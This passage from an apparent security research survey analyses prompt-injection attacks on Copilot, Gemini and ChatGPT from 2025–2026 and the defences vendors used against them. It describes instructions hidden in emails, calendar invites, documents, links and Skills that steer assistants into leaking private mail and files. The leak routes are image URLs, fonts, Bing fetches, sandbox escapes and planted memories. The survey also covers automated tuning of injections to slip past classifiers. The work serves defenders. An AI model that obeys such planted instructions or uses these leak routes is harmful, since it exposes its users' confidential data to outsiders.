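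Radware calls the email version zero-click and the file version one-click, because the user has to share the file with ChatGPT. By that standard, Zenity's poisoned document was also one-click. Radware reported its new attacks on 26 September 2025, OpenAI fixed them on 16 December, and Radware published on 8 January 2026. The publication date comes from Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

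### Calendar invitations in 2026

Later that month, Miggo Security published an attack on Gemini that kept the stolen data inside Google Calendar. Daily Security Review's *Google Calendar Invites Let Researchers Hijack Gemini in Stealthy Prompt-Injection Attack* describes an earlier demonstration in which instructions in a calendar invitation's title could make Gemini leak emails or control smart-home devices when the user asked about the day's schedule. Google said it had fixed the earlier flaw.

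Miggo put its instructions in the event's description instead, as SiliconANGLE's *Indirect prompt injection in Google Gemini enabled unauthorized access to meeting data* (2026) explains. When the user asked an ordinary question about their schedule, Gemini created a new event and wrote a summary of the user's private meetings in it. According to TechRadar's *A Google Gemini security flaw let hackers use calendar invites*, Miggo said many companies' calendar settings would let the attacker see the new event.

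The attack used no image or outside web address, so the fixes to Gemini's image handling could not have stopped it. The attacker did have to be able to see the new event, which was probably easier for an employee than for a stranger, because companies commonly let colleagues view one another's calendars. Miggo says Google has since mitigated the problem.

Adversa AI's *Google Workspace Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a rating page from a security vendor, still lists outsiders' emails, shared documents, invitations and chat messages among the default inputs to Gemini in Workspace. These all enter the same context, however much the company trusts the author. The page also lists CVE-2026-0628, but that flaw involves a malicious browser extension and needs no planted email or file.

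### Who can write what the assistant reads

These attacks differ in who can supply the text and in what brings it to the assistant's attention.

| Attack | Who could supply the text | What the victim did |
|---|---|---|
| Bard, 2023 | Anyone able to share a Google Doc with the victim | Brought up the document in Bard |
| GeminiJack, 2025 | Anyone able to email, invite or share a file with an employee | Searched for a related subject |
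| Zenity's ChatGPT attack, 2025 | Anyone whose file the victim would upload | Uploaded it and asked for a summary |
| ShadowLeak, 2025 | Anyone able to email the victim | Asked for research on the day's emails |
| Miggo's Gemini attack, 2026 | Anyone able to send a calendar invitation | Asked about their schedule |

Attackers have the most freedom with email because most companies have to accept it from strangers. With an uploaded file, the victim has a chance to be suspicious. However, Zenity Labs points out that a malicious employee could add hidden text to many of the company's own documents, which colleagues have no reason to distrust.

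Gemini Enterprise can index text from the widest group of people because its customers can connect products from other vendors. If a company connects its support system, for example, anyone who files a request may be able to add text to the index. An employee whose search retrieves that request may never use the support system and would not know that strangers can write there.

GeminiJack, like EchoLeak, required the attacker's text to match the employee's search. ShadowLeak was easier to carry out when the user asked for research on all of the day's emails, because the malicious email only had to arrive that day.

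## One-click links and code execution in Copilot, January to August 2026

Most of the attacks on Microsoft's Copilot products that researchers published between January and August 2026 required the victim to click a link, open a document or upload a file, unlike EchoLeak. They still matter for zero-click theft because the way instructions reach the model is largely independent of the way data gets out. Clicking a link only delivered the instructions, so any image or server that could then carry data out could in principle do the same when the instructions arrived by email.

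### A prompt inside a link

Many AI products accept a question as part of a web address. A link that ends in `?q=Hello` opens the chat page with "Hello" as the user's message, and some products answer it immediately. An attacker can replace "Hello" with a paragraph of instructions. The data security company Varonis calls this parameter-to-prompt injection.

A one-click link attack does not quite fit the definition of indirect prompt injection, because the model receives the attacker's instructions as the user's own request. Tags that separate the user's message from retrieved content would therefore give the attacker's text the more trusted label, and a filter that screens only retrieved content would not check it.

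Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) describes an attack on the consumer version of Copilot that began when the victim clicked a link. The link contained an instruction for Copilot to open an address on the attacker's server with the victim's name in it. The server replied with another instruction, such as to send the victim's location, and then another. The attacker could choose each instruction after reading the last response, so nobody could tell from the link what the attacker would take. Copilot removed sensitive text from outgoing addresses, but Varonis found that this safeguard covered only the first request. The theft continued even if the victim closed the tab.

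Varonis reported the flaw on 31 August 2025, and Microsoft patched it on 13 January 2026, according to BeyondMachines. An attacker could access data including the user's chat history and a record of the files the user had opened, according to iTnews' *Microsoft patches single-click Copilot data stealing attack*. The flaw did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot.

### SearchLeak

In June 2026, Taler, a researcher at Varonis, showed that a similar link worked on Microsoft 365 Copilot's Enterprise Search, the page where employees search their company's mail, calendars and files. The attack went as follows:

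1. The attacker sends an employee a link to Microsoft's real search page, with instructions in place of a search query.
2. The employee clicks the link. Copilot follows the instructions and searches the employee's mailbox.
3. Copilot starts writing an answer that contains an image. The image's address includes the subject line of an email it found.
4. The employee's browser requests the image from Bing.
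5. Bing's server contacts the attacker's server, and the subject line appears in the attacker's log.

The link led to a Microsoft domain, so a mail filter that judges links by their domain would probably have let it through.

Microsoft guarded against images in Copilot's answers by wrapping the model's output in a code block, which makes a browser show HTML as plain text. But it added the code block only after the model had finished writing. Copilot shows its answers piece by piece as the model produces them, so the browser requested the image before the code block was in place. This is a race condition, a flaw in which the result depends on which of two steps happens first. The attacker didn't need precise timing, because a browser can send a request in milliseconds while a model usually takes seconds to finish an answer. EchoLeak, by contrast, had used a form of Markdown that Copilot's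 filter did not recognise. Taler recommends cleaning the output before the browser renders it.

The page's Content Security Policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's own server, but it allowed every subdomain of bing.com. In Bing's search-by-image feature, the user supplies the address of a picture, and Bing's server fetches the picture to analyse it. The attacker supplied the address of their own server with the subject line included in it, which made this the same kind of server-side request forgery as the Teams route in EchoLeak. A year after Aim's report, Microsoft's allowlists evidently still included a server that fetches outside addresses.

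Rehberger's work on Copilot suggests why that is hard. Embrace The Red reports that the policy differed between sites where Copilot appears, such as its chat page, SharePoint and Excel Online. Some lists included test servers, and some entries contained what looked like employees' user names, as if staff had added their own domains. Rehberger concluded that Microsoft did not control the lists tightly and that nobody should rely on them to stop data theft from Copilot.

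### What SearchLeak could take

Taler's published example extracted the subject line of one email, which is less than Varonis's headline claims suggest. A subject line can still give a thief a login code, because some services put one there. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that such codes often remain valid for several minutes. The thief would usually need the victim's password as well.

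Taler also lists meeting notes, salary information and acquisition plans. Copilot searched with the employee's permissions, so it could probably have retrieved these, though the length of a web address would have limited how much data each image could carry.

Taler writes that all three flaws were necessary, and that without the prompt in the link an attacker could not have put HTML into Copilot's answer. This seems too strong, because in EchoLeak an email that Copilot retrieved had put an image into the answer. An email that got past the XPIA classifier and matched the employee's question might also have exploited the late safeguard and the Bing route. Taler does not report trying this, but the three attacks in *ReLeak*, which Simonovich published that December, started from emails.

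### A critical flaw with a medium score

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the official record of SearchLeak, appeared on 4 June, eleven days before Varonis's report. By then Microsoft had fixed the flaw on its own servers. The record reports no exploitation. It rates the flaw "Critical" but gives it a CVSS score of 6.5, which is in the medium range.

The two ratings come from different scales. "Critical" is Microsoft's own severity label and plays no part in the CVSS formula. Microsoft's CVSS vector for SearchLeak matches the one the National Vulnerability Database gave EchoLeak, except that SearchLeak requires the user to act, which lowers the score from 7.5 to 6.5. Even without the click, the score would have been well short of critical on the CVSS scale. Microsoft does not explain its label in the record, but it was presumably thinking of how much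 a thief could read.

The label does little to help a security team set priorities, because Microsoft also applied it to ShareLeak, which scored 7.5, and to another Copilot flaw that scored 5.3.

The National Vulnerability Database gave SearchLeak its higher score, 7.5, on the assumption that no user had to act. The database added this score on 8 June, a week before Varonis published the details, according to the change history on CVEfeed. The Next Web mistakenly reported the database's score as 6.5, possibly because the database displays Microsoft's vector alongside its own.

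### A shared document and a font

Rehberger found the flaw that scored 5.3, which came closer to being zero-click than SearchLeak did. In autumn 2025 he noticed that Copilot could show a preview of a web page inside its answer. Copilot removed ordinary images from the preview, but a page can also load a font from another server, and the Content Security Policy restricted fonts less than images.

In the demonstration Embrace The Red describes, the victim opens a shared Word document and types "hi there" to Copilot. Instructions in the document make Copilot find a particular email, put its contents in the address of a font and display the preview. When the browser requests the font, the attacker receives the email's contents. The same approach worked in Word's desktop version and in Excel Online.

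Rehberger calls this a zero-click attack because the victim only uses Copilot normally. Under the stricter definition it is not, since the victim has opened the attacker's document. Microsoft's vector, which STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026) reproduces, also lists user interaction as required. Microsoft rates the attack as complex to carry out, which accounts for the entire difference between its score and SearchLeak's. The complexity rating is harder to understand, because Rehberger describes the final version of the attack as reliable.

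Rehberger reported the channel on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it on 5 March 2026. His attack is the best evidence from this period that a planted document could exploit a newly discovered data exfiltration channel as well as a prompt typed by the victim could.

### CoSnitch and stored memory

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes another one-click attack on consumer Copilot. According to Varonis, a prompt in a link only filled in the question box, and the user had to press Enter to run it. The researchers asked Copilot why such a prompt could not run by itself. Its answer included an undocumented setting, described as disabled by Microsoft. When the researchers added the setting to a link, the prompt ran as soon as the page opened.

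Varonis calls this way of finding flaws "meta-hacking" and says it makes CoSnitch unique. Chatbots often describe their own software incorrectly, so testing the answer was the useful part. Microsoft credits two other finders besides the Varonis researcher, one of them a Microsoft employee, but does not say in its record how they found the flaw.

Once the prompt ran, it could make Copilot search the user's connected apps, such as Gmail, Google Drive and Google Calendar. Copilot then put the results in a web address and opened it with the feature it uses to summarise web pages. As in ShadowLeak, the request did not come from the user's browser, so no Content Security Policy applied. In one test, Copilot retrieved an email that contained a password in plain text.

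Varonis says the attack "exfiltrates data from enterprises", but Microsoft's record lists the affected product as Copilot Web, and the tests used Copilot Personal. Company data was at risk only if an employee had connected a work account or pasted work material into a chat. Without connected apps, the attacker could reach only what the victim had shared with Copilot, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*.

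The third flaw in CoSnitch involved Copilot's memory, the notes it keeps about a user from one conversation to the next. When a user asked Copilot to summarise a web page, hidden text on the page could add a note of the attacker's choosing. The note then influenced every later conversation until the user found and deleted it, even if the user changed their password. In a demonstration, Varonis planted a false note that a known security flaw posed no risk. Varonis also writes that a note could make Copilot forward its answers to an attacker, but does not demonstrate this.

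Rehberger had shown that a document could plant a lasting instruction in Microsoft 365 Copilot's memory. He used a biography of Albert Einstein with instructions hidden in the middle. After summarising it, Copilot asked whether the information had been helpful, and answering either "yes" or "no" made it save a note. From then on, whenever the user gave Copilot a password or code, even one created after the upload, Copilot displayed a preview that sent the secret out in the web address of a font. Embrace The Red reports that Microsoft fixed the planting of memories in December 2025. As of April 2026, Microsoft's documentation stated that changes to memory left no entry in a customer's audit logs, so an administrator could not have searched those logs for planted notes.

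People outside security research already use links to plant notes. Microsoft found numerous attempts on public web pages, including "Summarize with AI" buttons whose links also contained an instruction to recommend a particular company. These attempts were promotional, but they used the same delivery method as data theft.

Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft shipped the patches eight months later, on 18 August 2026. That is a long time to patch a one-click flaw, and longer than Microsoft took to fix EchoLeak. Neither company knew of any exploitation.

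Microsoft scored CoSnitch at 8.8, well above SearchLeak, although SearchLeak exposed company mail directly. Both vectors describe a one-click attack of low complexity, but Microsoft also rated the losses of integrity and availability as high for CoSnitch. The planted notes justify the integrity rating. Nothing in Varonis's account explains the availability rating, since the attack did not stop anyone from using Copilot. Without the loss of availability, the score would be 8.1.

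### ChatMate

In the earlier attacks, Copilot could send data out only through features Microsoft had built for other purposes, such as displaying images or fetching web pages. By 2026, Copilot could also run programs in a code interpreter, which AI assistants use to do calculations, read documents and build spreadsheets. An attacker who can get their own program to run there can have it send requests and act on the replies, without relying on the model to write an address correctly each time.

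Vendors therefore run this code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that is supposed to have no route to the attacker. The sandbox serves the same purpose as the Content Security Policy in the browser. In 2026, two security companies found ways out of the sandboxes around Microsoft's assistants.

*Phantom Keystrokes* (Fiehler, 2026) describes ChatMate, an attack developed by Rubrik, which sells data security products. An employee could trigger the attack by uploading a Word document for an ordinary task. Invisible white text in the document made the assistant run the attacker's code, which escaped from the sandbox and opened a two-way connection. The attacker could then send prompts into the employee's live session, read the answers, and access whatever the assistant could reach for that employee, such as email, files and chat history.

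Zenity had called its 2024 attack "RCE", although it only influenced what Copilot searched for and wrote. ChatMate, by contrast, ran an outsider's program on a Microsoft server. It was not strictly zero-click, because the employee had to upload the attacker's file.

Fiehler does not name the assistant, but *AI sandbox escape uncovered in Microsoft Copilot flaw* (Villamil, 2026) identifies it as Copilot and reports that Rubrik found the problem in February 2026 and Microsoft patched it by mid-March. Joe Hladik, who leads Rubrik's research group, said in an interview that the attack would give control over the files of "probably hundreds, thousands, or much more" users. Fiehler describes one employee's session and access, so Hladik's larger figure looks like an estimate of what an attacker who controlled the server might reach. Rubrik also announced a product for governing AI agents that week.

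Microsoft published the official record, *Azure Kubernetes Service (AKS) Remote Code Execution Vulnerability*, on 9 June as CVE-2026-32193. It credits Ori Lahav of Rubrik, who presented ChatMate at the Black Hat conference in August. The record does not mention Copilot. Azure Kubernetes Service is the part of Microsoft's cloud that runs customers' programs in isolated containers. The score of 8.8 measures how serious the flaw is if an attacker can already run code in a container, not the risk from a malicious Word document.

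The record also lists customer action as required. This applies to companies that run their own programs on the service, which need to install the new version. Companies that only used Copilot had nothing to install, and a search for Copilot flaws would not have found this one.

### Copilot Cowork

Copilot Cowork is an agent in Microsoft 365 that carries out longer tasks across Outlook, Teams, SharePoint and connected products. Users can extend it with Skills, which are files of instructions that may come with scripts for the agent to run. Users often find Skills online and upload them.

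PromptArmor's *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control* describes a malicious Skill for comparing documents. When the user asks Cowork to check a contract against a proposal, the Skill produces a genuine report, but one of the Skill's scripts also connects to the attacker's server, runs the commands it receives and returns the results. In the demonstration, the attacker listed the user's Outlook messages and read an email thread about a business deal. The attacker could also have accessed SharePoint files, chat history and data from plugins. Pressing the stop button ended the agent's turn but not the script. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft had mitigated it by 19 August.

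This was partly a conventional attack, since the user had installed a stranger's program. But a sandbox is meant to limit the damage such a program can do, and PromptArmor says a prompt injection could have used the same route out of the sandbox if it got Cowork to run the code. An injection could come from a document or email the user had not chosen.

PromptArmor had published a different attack on Cowork in May that did not require escaping the sandbox. Microsoft's documentation says Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that Cowork did not ask when the recipient was the user. Instructions in an uploaded Skill made Cowork send the user a Teams message containing images from the attacker's server. When the user opened the message, Teams loaded the images, which sent the attacker any data Cowork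 had put in the image URLs.

Cowork had put download links there. Microsoft 365 can create these links, which let anyone who has one download a file without logging in. An image address can hold only a little text, which limited what the attacker could take in Rehberger's attack on Bard and in EchoLeak. A download link is short enough to fit in an image address, and it gives the attacker the entire file.

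The attack succeeded in all five of PromptArmor's trials. By the calculation used for ShadowLeak, this is consistent with a true success rate as low as 55%. When PromptArmor selected Claude Opus 4.7, a more capable model, instead of letting Cowork choose, the agent searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents.

The user in this attack had asked Cowork to summarize the week's work. Cowork can also run such a task unattended on a schedule, in which case the user would only need to open a message from their own assistant. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, cites the case as an example of how keeping attackers from getting data out remains the biggest challenge in designing agents. PromptArmor treated the problem as a design risk rather than a single bug, and reported no fix.

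| Attack | Trigger | User action | Channel | Repair date |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reprompt | Prompt in a link | Clicked the link | Copilot opened the attacker's address | 13 January 2026 |
| Rehberger's font attack | Shared Word document | Opened it and typed to Copilot | Font in a page preview | 5 March 2026 |
| ChatMate | Hidden text in a Word document | Uploaded the document | Connection from a Microsoft server | By mid-March 2026 |
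| SearchLeak | Prompt in a link | Clicked the link | Image request through Bing | By 4 June 2026 |
| CoSnitch | Prompt in a link | Clicked the link | Copilot opened the attacker's address | 18 August 2026 |
| Cowork, May report | Instructions in a Skill | Uploaded the Skill, used it and opened a message | Images in a Teams message | None reported |
| Cowork, sandbox flaw | Script in a Skill | Uploaded the Skill and used it | Connection from the sandbox | By 19 August 2026 |

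## ReLeak: three zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2026

On 3 December 2026, Cato AI Labs published three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which it calls ReLeak, that needed neither a click nor an uploaded file. Microsoft had already fixed all three flaws. The same team found EchoLeak when it was called Aim Labs and belonged to Aim Security. Cato Networks bought Aim in September 2025, according to *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026).

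### One unread email

All three attacks begin as EchoLeak did. An outsider sends an employee an email containing instructions. When the employee later asks Copilot an ordinary work question, Copilot retrieves the email while looking for an answer, treats the instructions as part of its task, and collects confidential information that the employee is allowed to read. The employee does not open the email, follow a link or approve a permission, according to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026).

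Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) says that the theft needed no action by the user, but it also describes the employee asking Copilot a question. That question has to lead Copilot to the attacker's email. Aim solved this problem in 2025 by covering many workplace subjects in one long message. It is unclear whether Cato did the same, so it is not known how often an ordinary question would have triggered ReLeak.

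Copilot seems to have collected the confidential information after reading the email. If it ran a new search, as Gemini Enterprise did in GeminiJack, ReLeak could reach more data than EchoLeak, which took only what was already in the context.

Microsoft's XPIA classifiers, the filters meant to keep injected instructions away from the model, stopped none of the three attacks. Colantuoni (2026) explains in *ReLeak: furto di dati tramite Microsoft 365 Copilot* that Copilot does not carry out blunt commands from an email, but instructions that looked like legitimate requests got through. Aim's email had similarly passed the filters because it read like a set of tasks for the employee.

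Cato's researchers directed AI agents to find wording that worked. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, reports that the agents generated test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. The number of refusals isn't public. For EchoLeak, the team had spent about three months reverse-engineering Copilot.

Automated testing makes it less useful for Microsoft to block any one wording. If a filter stops 99 out of 100 differently worded emails, an attacker needs a hundred tries on average, which a program can easily make. The attacker can also run the tests on their own Copilot account, where failed attempts don't alert anyone at the target company.

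### An image fetched through Bing

In the first attack (CVE-2026-124115), Copilot writes an answer containing a Markdown image whose URL includes the confidential text. The employee's browser automatically loads the image by sending a request to Bing, and Bing's server then passes the text to the attacker's server.

SC Media describes the same use of Bing in SearchLeak, which needed one click and which Microsoft had fixed by 4 June. Cato sent its reports to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August, so data could still leave through Bing at least 55 days after that fix. SearchLeak also depended on two other flaws, and repairing either would have stopped it. Microsoft most likely did that and left Bing unchanged, although Cato may have found a different Bing feature that did the same thing.

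Microsoft fixed this flaw last, on 15 November.

### A link in a file that Copilot made

In the second attack (CVE-2026-124132), Copilot creates a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link whose address includes the confidential text, then saves the file to OneDrive or SharePoint. Microsoft software running in the background processes the file and fetches the link, so the attack does not depend on what the employee's browser displays.

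According to Pixel Magazine, the request in Cato's tests arrived one to eight minutes after the chat ended, and nobody had opened the file. Closing the chat would therefore not have stopped the theft.

It is unclear which background process fetched the link. Cloud storage services often open links to build previews or check for malware, and either would explain the delay. Slack's link previews created a similar risk in 2024.

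As in ShadowLeak, the request bypassed both the Content Security Policy and any company logs of employees' web traffic. But this attack probably left better evidence than the other two. Unless somebody deleted it, the file would still be in storage, and its link would contain the attacker's address and the stolen text. A company could check by searching files that Copilot created before 11 November, when Microsoft fixed the flaw, for links to unfamiliar domains.

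### Code that reached the internet

Antipov reports that Copilot's code interpreter runs Python programs in a sandbox, and that Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves it. In the third attack (CVE-2026-78501), however, Copilot ran code that sent confidential data directly to an outside server.

This attack needed no image or link, and no other Microsoft service to relay the data. A program can also send far more data than fits in a web address, though it is unclear how much Cato extracted.

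*Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026) describes an earlier escape from Copilot's sandbox by another company, Rubrik. It was published on 6 August, while Cato was still submitting its reports. Microsoft had patched Rubrik's escape by mid-March, so the sandbox failed again within about five months of a repair. Rubrik's attack required an uploaded document, whereas Cato's needed only an unread email.

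Agents that customers build with Copilot Studio or the simpler Agent Builder can also use the interpreter. Nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected these agents. It would have been more serious in them, because an incoming email can start some of them without anyone asking a question, as Zenity showed with its copy of McKinsey's agent.

Microsoft fixed the interpreter flaw first, on 17 September.

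### One score and two empty records

Microsoft raised the interpreter flaw's CVSS score from 7.4 to 8.6. It also rated the flaw "Critical", which, as with SearchLeak, is Microsoft's own label and not the CVSS rating.

The change from 7.4 to 8.6 has a likely explanation. Suppose that an outsider can exploit the flaw over a network with little difficulty, that the scope changes, and that the only damage is a high loss of confidentiality. The impact figure is then about 3.99. If a user has to take part, the exploitability figure is about 2.84, and the score is

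$$1.08 \times (3.99 + 2.84) \approx 7.38$$

which rounds up to 7.4. If no user has to take part, exploitability rises to 3.89:

$$1.08 \times (3.99 + 3.89) \approx 8.51$$

This rounds up to 8.6. So Microsoft probably assumed at first that the attack required some action by the victim, and later accepted that asking Copilot an ordinary question doesn't count as one. This is an inference, because other combinations of answers also produce 7.4 and 8.6. If it is right, Microsoft rated the flaw the same way as EchoLeak, except that it left out the low loss of integrity that had raised EchoLeak's score to 9.3.

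The other two flaws had no confirmed public score when Cato published. Faisal reports that two of the three CVE numbers, presumably those for the Bing and file flaws, were still marked "reserved", meaning that the numbers existed but the full records had not appeared. Microsoft had published EchoLeak's record on the same day as Aim's research, but a security team that looked up the Bing flaw on 3 December, 18 days after the repair, would have found an empty entry.

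Microsoft made the fixes on its own servers, and its advisory says customers need not do anything, according to Faisal. Pixel Magazine is misleading when it says the problem is solved for those who keep Microsoft 365 up to date, because customers had no update to install.

Cato says it knows of no affected customers and no real attacks. The summary at the top of Faisal's article attributes the statement that no customers were affected to Microsoft, but the body attributes it to Cato. Cato can't see Microsoft's logs, so its statement means only that nobody had told it of a theft.

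### EchoLeak and ReLeak compared

| Attack | What contacted the attacker's server | Microsoft's CVSS score | Fixed | Days from report to fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Teams preview service | 9.3 | May 2025 | 90 to 150 |
| ReLeak, image | Bing | Not confirmed | 15 November 2026 | 87 to 109 |
| ReLeak, file | Microsoft's background processing | Not confirmed | 11 November 2026 | 83 to 105 |
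| ReLeak, code | Program in Copilot's sandbox | 8.6 | 17 September 2026 | 28 to 50 |

The last column gives ranges because only the month of the EchoLeak report is public, and only the first and last of Cato's three reports have public dates.

The email got past Microsoft's first two defences in both years. The XPIA classifier let through instructions written as office requests, and the model then followed them. Antipov writes that Microsoft changed its protections after EchoLeak but that Copilot could still take instructions from an untrusted source as part of its task.

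The next defence is the filter that removes outside links and images from Copilot's answers. Ravia's team got past it in 2025 with a lesser-known form of Markdown. An image got through again in 2026, and it is unclear whether Cato also used an unusual notation. The filter may instead have accepted the image's Bing address because Bing belongs to Microsoft.

Next is the browser's list of allowed domains, where Microsoft seems to have repeated a mistake. In EchoLeak, the list allowed a Teams address that fetched an outside page, and in ReLeak, the browser could reach a Bing address that did the same. Removing one such address does little good if another remains, and Microsoft runs many services that fetch content from the web.

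The file and code attacks have no counterpart in EchoLeak. The browser did not send the data, so neither attack had to get past the browser's list. Faisal points out that each ability Copilot gained, such as writing files or running code, became a new way for data to leave. A customer who blocked every outside image from Copilot's answers could still have lost data through these two routes.

Microsoft repaired the interpreter flaw in four to seven weeks, much faster than EchoLeak. The other two repairs took about three months or a little more, which may have been anywhere from two months faster to a few weeks slower than EchoLeak's. The interpreter may have been quicker to repair because its sandbox was never supposed to have network access, so Microsoft only had to restore that restriction. Bing and the background software are supposed to fetch things from the internet, so Microsoft had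 to decide which requests to refuse without breaking the feature for other users.

### "Too little progress"

Cato says that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. It has a commercial interest in that conclusion, because it benefits if companies decide that Microsoft's own safeguards are not enough. The site that carries Simonovich's report also advertises AI red teaming, which means attacking a customer's AI systems to find their weaknesses, and protection for AI agents. Cato's use of AI agents to find ReLeak is a good advertisement for its testing service.

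Microsoft does not appear to have answered the criticism. Its advisory deals only with the repairs.

The verdict is fair about injection. An email from a stranger could still direct Copilot more than a year after Microsoft fixed EchoLeak, and the same style of writing still worked. The use of Bing makes this look worse, because SearchLeak had already shown Microsoft that data could leave through Bing.

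It is less fair as a judgement on all the work of Microsoft's engineers, who repaired the most direct of the three routes within weeks. Cato also had to find new ways to get data out, which suggests that the Teams route it had used in EchoLeak no longer worked. And Microsoft was defending a product that could do more than it could in early 2025, so its defences could have improved even if the number of successful attacks stayed the same.

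Three successful attacks don't show whether Copilot has become harder to attack. It would be more useful to compare how many emails the team had to write before one worked in 2025 and in 2026. Ravia gave no such figure for EchoLeak. Cato's AI agents presumably logged every refusal in 2026, so Cato could at least publish the figure for that year.

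## Detection, blocked outputs and information-flow control

The month after Aim published EchoLeak, Microsoft described how it defends its products against indirect prompt injection. It distinguishes two kinds of defence. A probabilistic defence, such as a classifier, makes an attack less likely to work. A deterministic defence, such as a filter that removes every external image from an answer, guarantees that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences, but says detecting injected instructions with certainty is still an open research problem. It therefore assumes that some injections will succeed and tries to keep them from doing damage.

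### Before the model answers

A vendor's first chance to stop a malicious email comes before delivery. In July 2026 Microsoft added a prompt injection filter to Defender for Office 365, its email security product. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) explains that Defender treats these emails as high-confidence phishing and quarantines them, so Copilot cannot retrieve them. According to a notice from Microsoft (2026), the filter is on by default for customers with a Defender Plan 2 or Microsoft 365 E5 licence. It was still in public preview that July. Cato began reporting the ReLeak attacks later that month, but it is unclear whether its test mailboxes had the filter.

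Classifiers can next detect an attack when the assistant retrieves an email. Microsoft trains its Prompt Shields detector on known attacks in several languages. The detector only flags attacks, and the application has to block the text or respond in some other way. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes similar classifiers for Gemini, which leaves suspicious items out of its answer or refuses to answer. EchoLeak's email got past Microsoft's XPIA classifier because it read like ordinary office mail.

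Text that passes the classifiers enters the context, where Microsoft can mark it as untrusted using a technique it calls spotlighting. There are three versions:

| Version | "Please reply today" becomes |
|---|---|
| Delimiting | `<<Please reply today>>` |
| Datamarking | `Please^reply^today` |
| Encoding | `UGxlYXNlIHJlcGx5IHRvZGF5` |

In practice, the delimiters are random so that an attacker can't easily imitate them. The encoding is Base64, which the model can decode. In each version, the system prompt tells the model not to follow any instructions in the marked text. Google's equivalent, "security thought reinforcement", surrounds the content with reminders to do the user's task and ignore hostile instructions. These measures work only if the model follows the instructions they give it.

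Vendors also train the model to resist these attacks. SecurityWeek reports that Google fine-tuned Gemini 2.5 on automatically generated attacks so that it would ignore the planted instruction and answer the user's original request.

### After the model answers

Microsoft says that after Rehberger's report it deterministically blocked data theft through images and then looked for variants, including certain untrusted links, but EchoLeak and SearchLeak show that it missed some.

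Google wrote in June 2025 that the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace do not display outside images, so EchoLeak's image route was "not applicable". About a week earlier, Noma had probably reported GeminiJack, an attack that used an outside image to steal data from Gemini Enterprise. Google may have been right about the products it named, but a deterministic block protects only the products that include it.

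Gemini also removes links that Google's Safe Browsing service flags as dangerous. This is weaker than removing all outside links, because an attacker can register a new domain that the service has not flagged.

Both companies rely partly on the user to approve actions. Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, but the user has to send it. Gemini may prompt the user for confirmation before it deletes a calendar event.

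By April 2026 Google controlled several of these measures from one policy engine. Gavish lists rules for web addresses, tool calls and "tool chaining", the last of which presumably limit which tools Gemini can use in sequence. Engineers can change a rule faster than they can retrain a classifier. Google tests each improvement by simulating attacks on apps such as Gmail and Docs with the defence on and off, but Gavish gives no success rates.

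### Attackers who adapt

Until 2025 most researchers tested their defences against fixed lists of old attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues let the attacker learn from each attempt. In one of their methods, a program tried several injections, kept the most promising and had a language model rewrite them for the next round. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked twelve published defences and beat most of them more than 90% of the time.

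With Spotlighting, fixed attacks succeeded about 1% of the time, but the adaptive attack succeeded more than 95% of the time. Over 500 participants in a competition found another 265 injections that worked against Spotlighting. The adaptive attack also succeeded over 90% of the time against three classifiers, including Google's commercial Model Armor, and 71% of the time against a fourth, PIGuard. One successful injection was disguised as a company policy that required deleting a file whenever someone moved a meeting. As with EchoLeak's email, a filter strict enough to catch this would also block genuine mail.

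However, the program could see how confident each classifier was, which a stranger emailing a company can't. In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) told the attacker only whether an injection had worked. PIGuard had stopped every fixed attack on an agent built on GPT-4o-mini, but 28% of the adaptive attacks succeeded. That is still far too many for a company to rely on the classifier alone.

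Ma and colleagues also found that attacks succeeded much more often when the user told the agent to act on the content without specifying the action, for example by asking it to do whatever an email required. Employees often delegate work this way.

Attacks succeed less often against newer models. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) report that fewer than 1% of the attacks people had written for a public competition worked on recent Gemini models. The Google DeepMind team then had groups of AI agents attack models in 100 new scenarios and share notes on what had worked. The agents tried to make the model call a harmless but irrelevant tool, so that the model's security knowledge would not help. The strongest groups succeeded against even the most robust models tested. Google had switched off the defences outside its Gemini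 models, so its products should resist attacks better than the models did alone. But every model did worse as the attacking agents became more capable, so current defences may fail as attackers improve.

### Why stopping most attempts is not enough

A filter that stops 95% of attacks will probably let one through if the attacker sends 20 different emails, as calculated earlier for guardrails. Stopping 99.9% is not enough either. If each email's chance is independent of the others, an attacker who writes once to each of 1,000 employees gets at least one through with a probability of

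$$1 - 0.999^{1000} \approx 0.63$$

No single employee would receive a suspicious number of messages.

Real attack attempts aren't quite independent, but *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) found that they were close to independent in a small open model. Attacks on that model succeeded 86% of the time within three attempts and 99.6% within ten. Resending the same text was less effective, succeeding 94% of the time within ten attempts.

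*BrowseSafe++* (2026) shows how inaccurate the formula can be. It tested web-browsing agents on 1,024 tasks, first with a fixed injection and then with up to 64 attempts that adapted to the agent's responses.

| Model | Success with the fixed injection | Formula's prediction for 64 attempts | Actual success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sonnet 5 | 2.05% | 73% | 31% |
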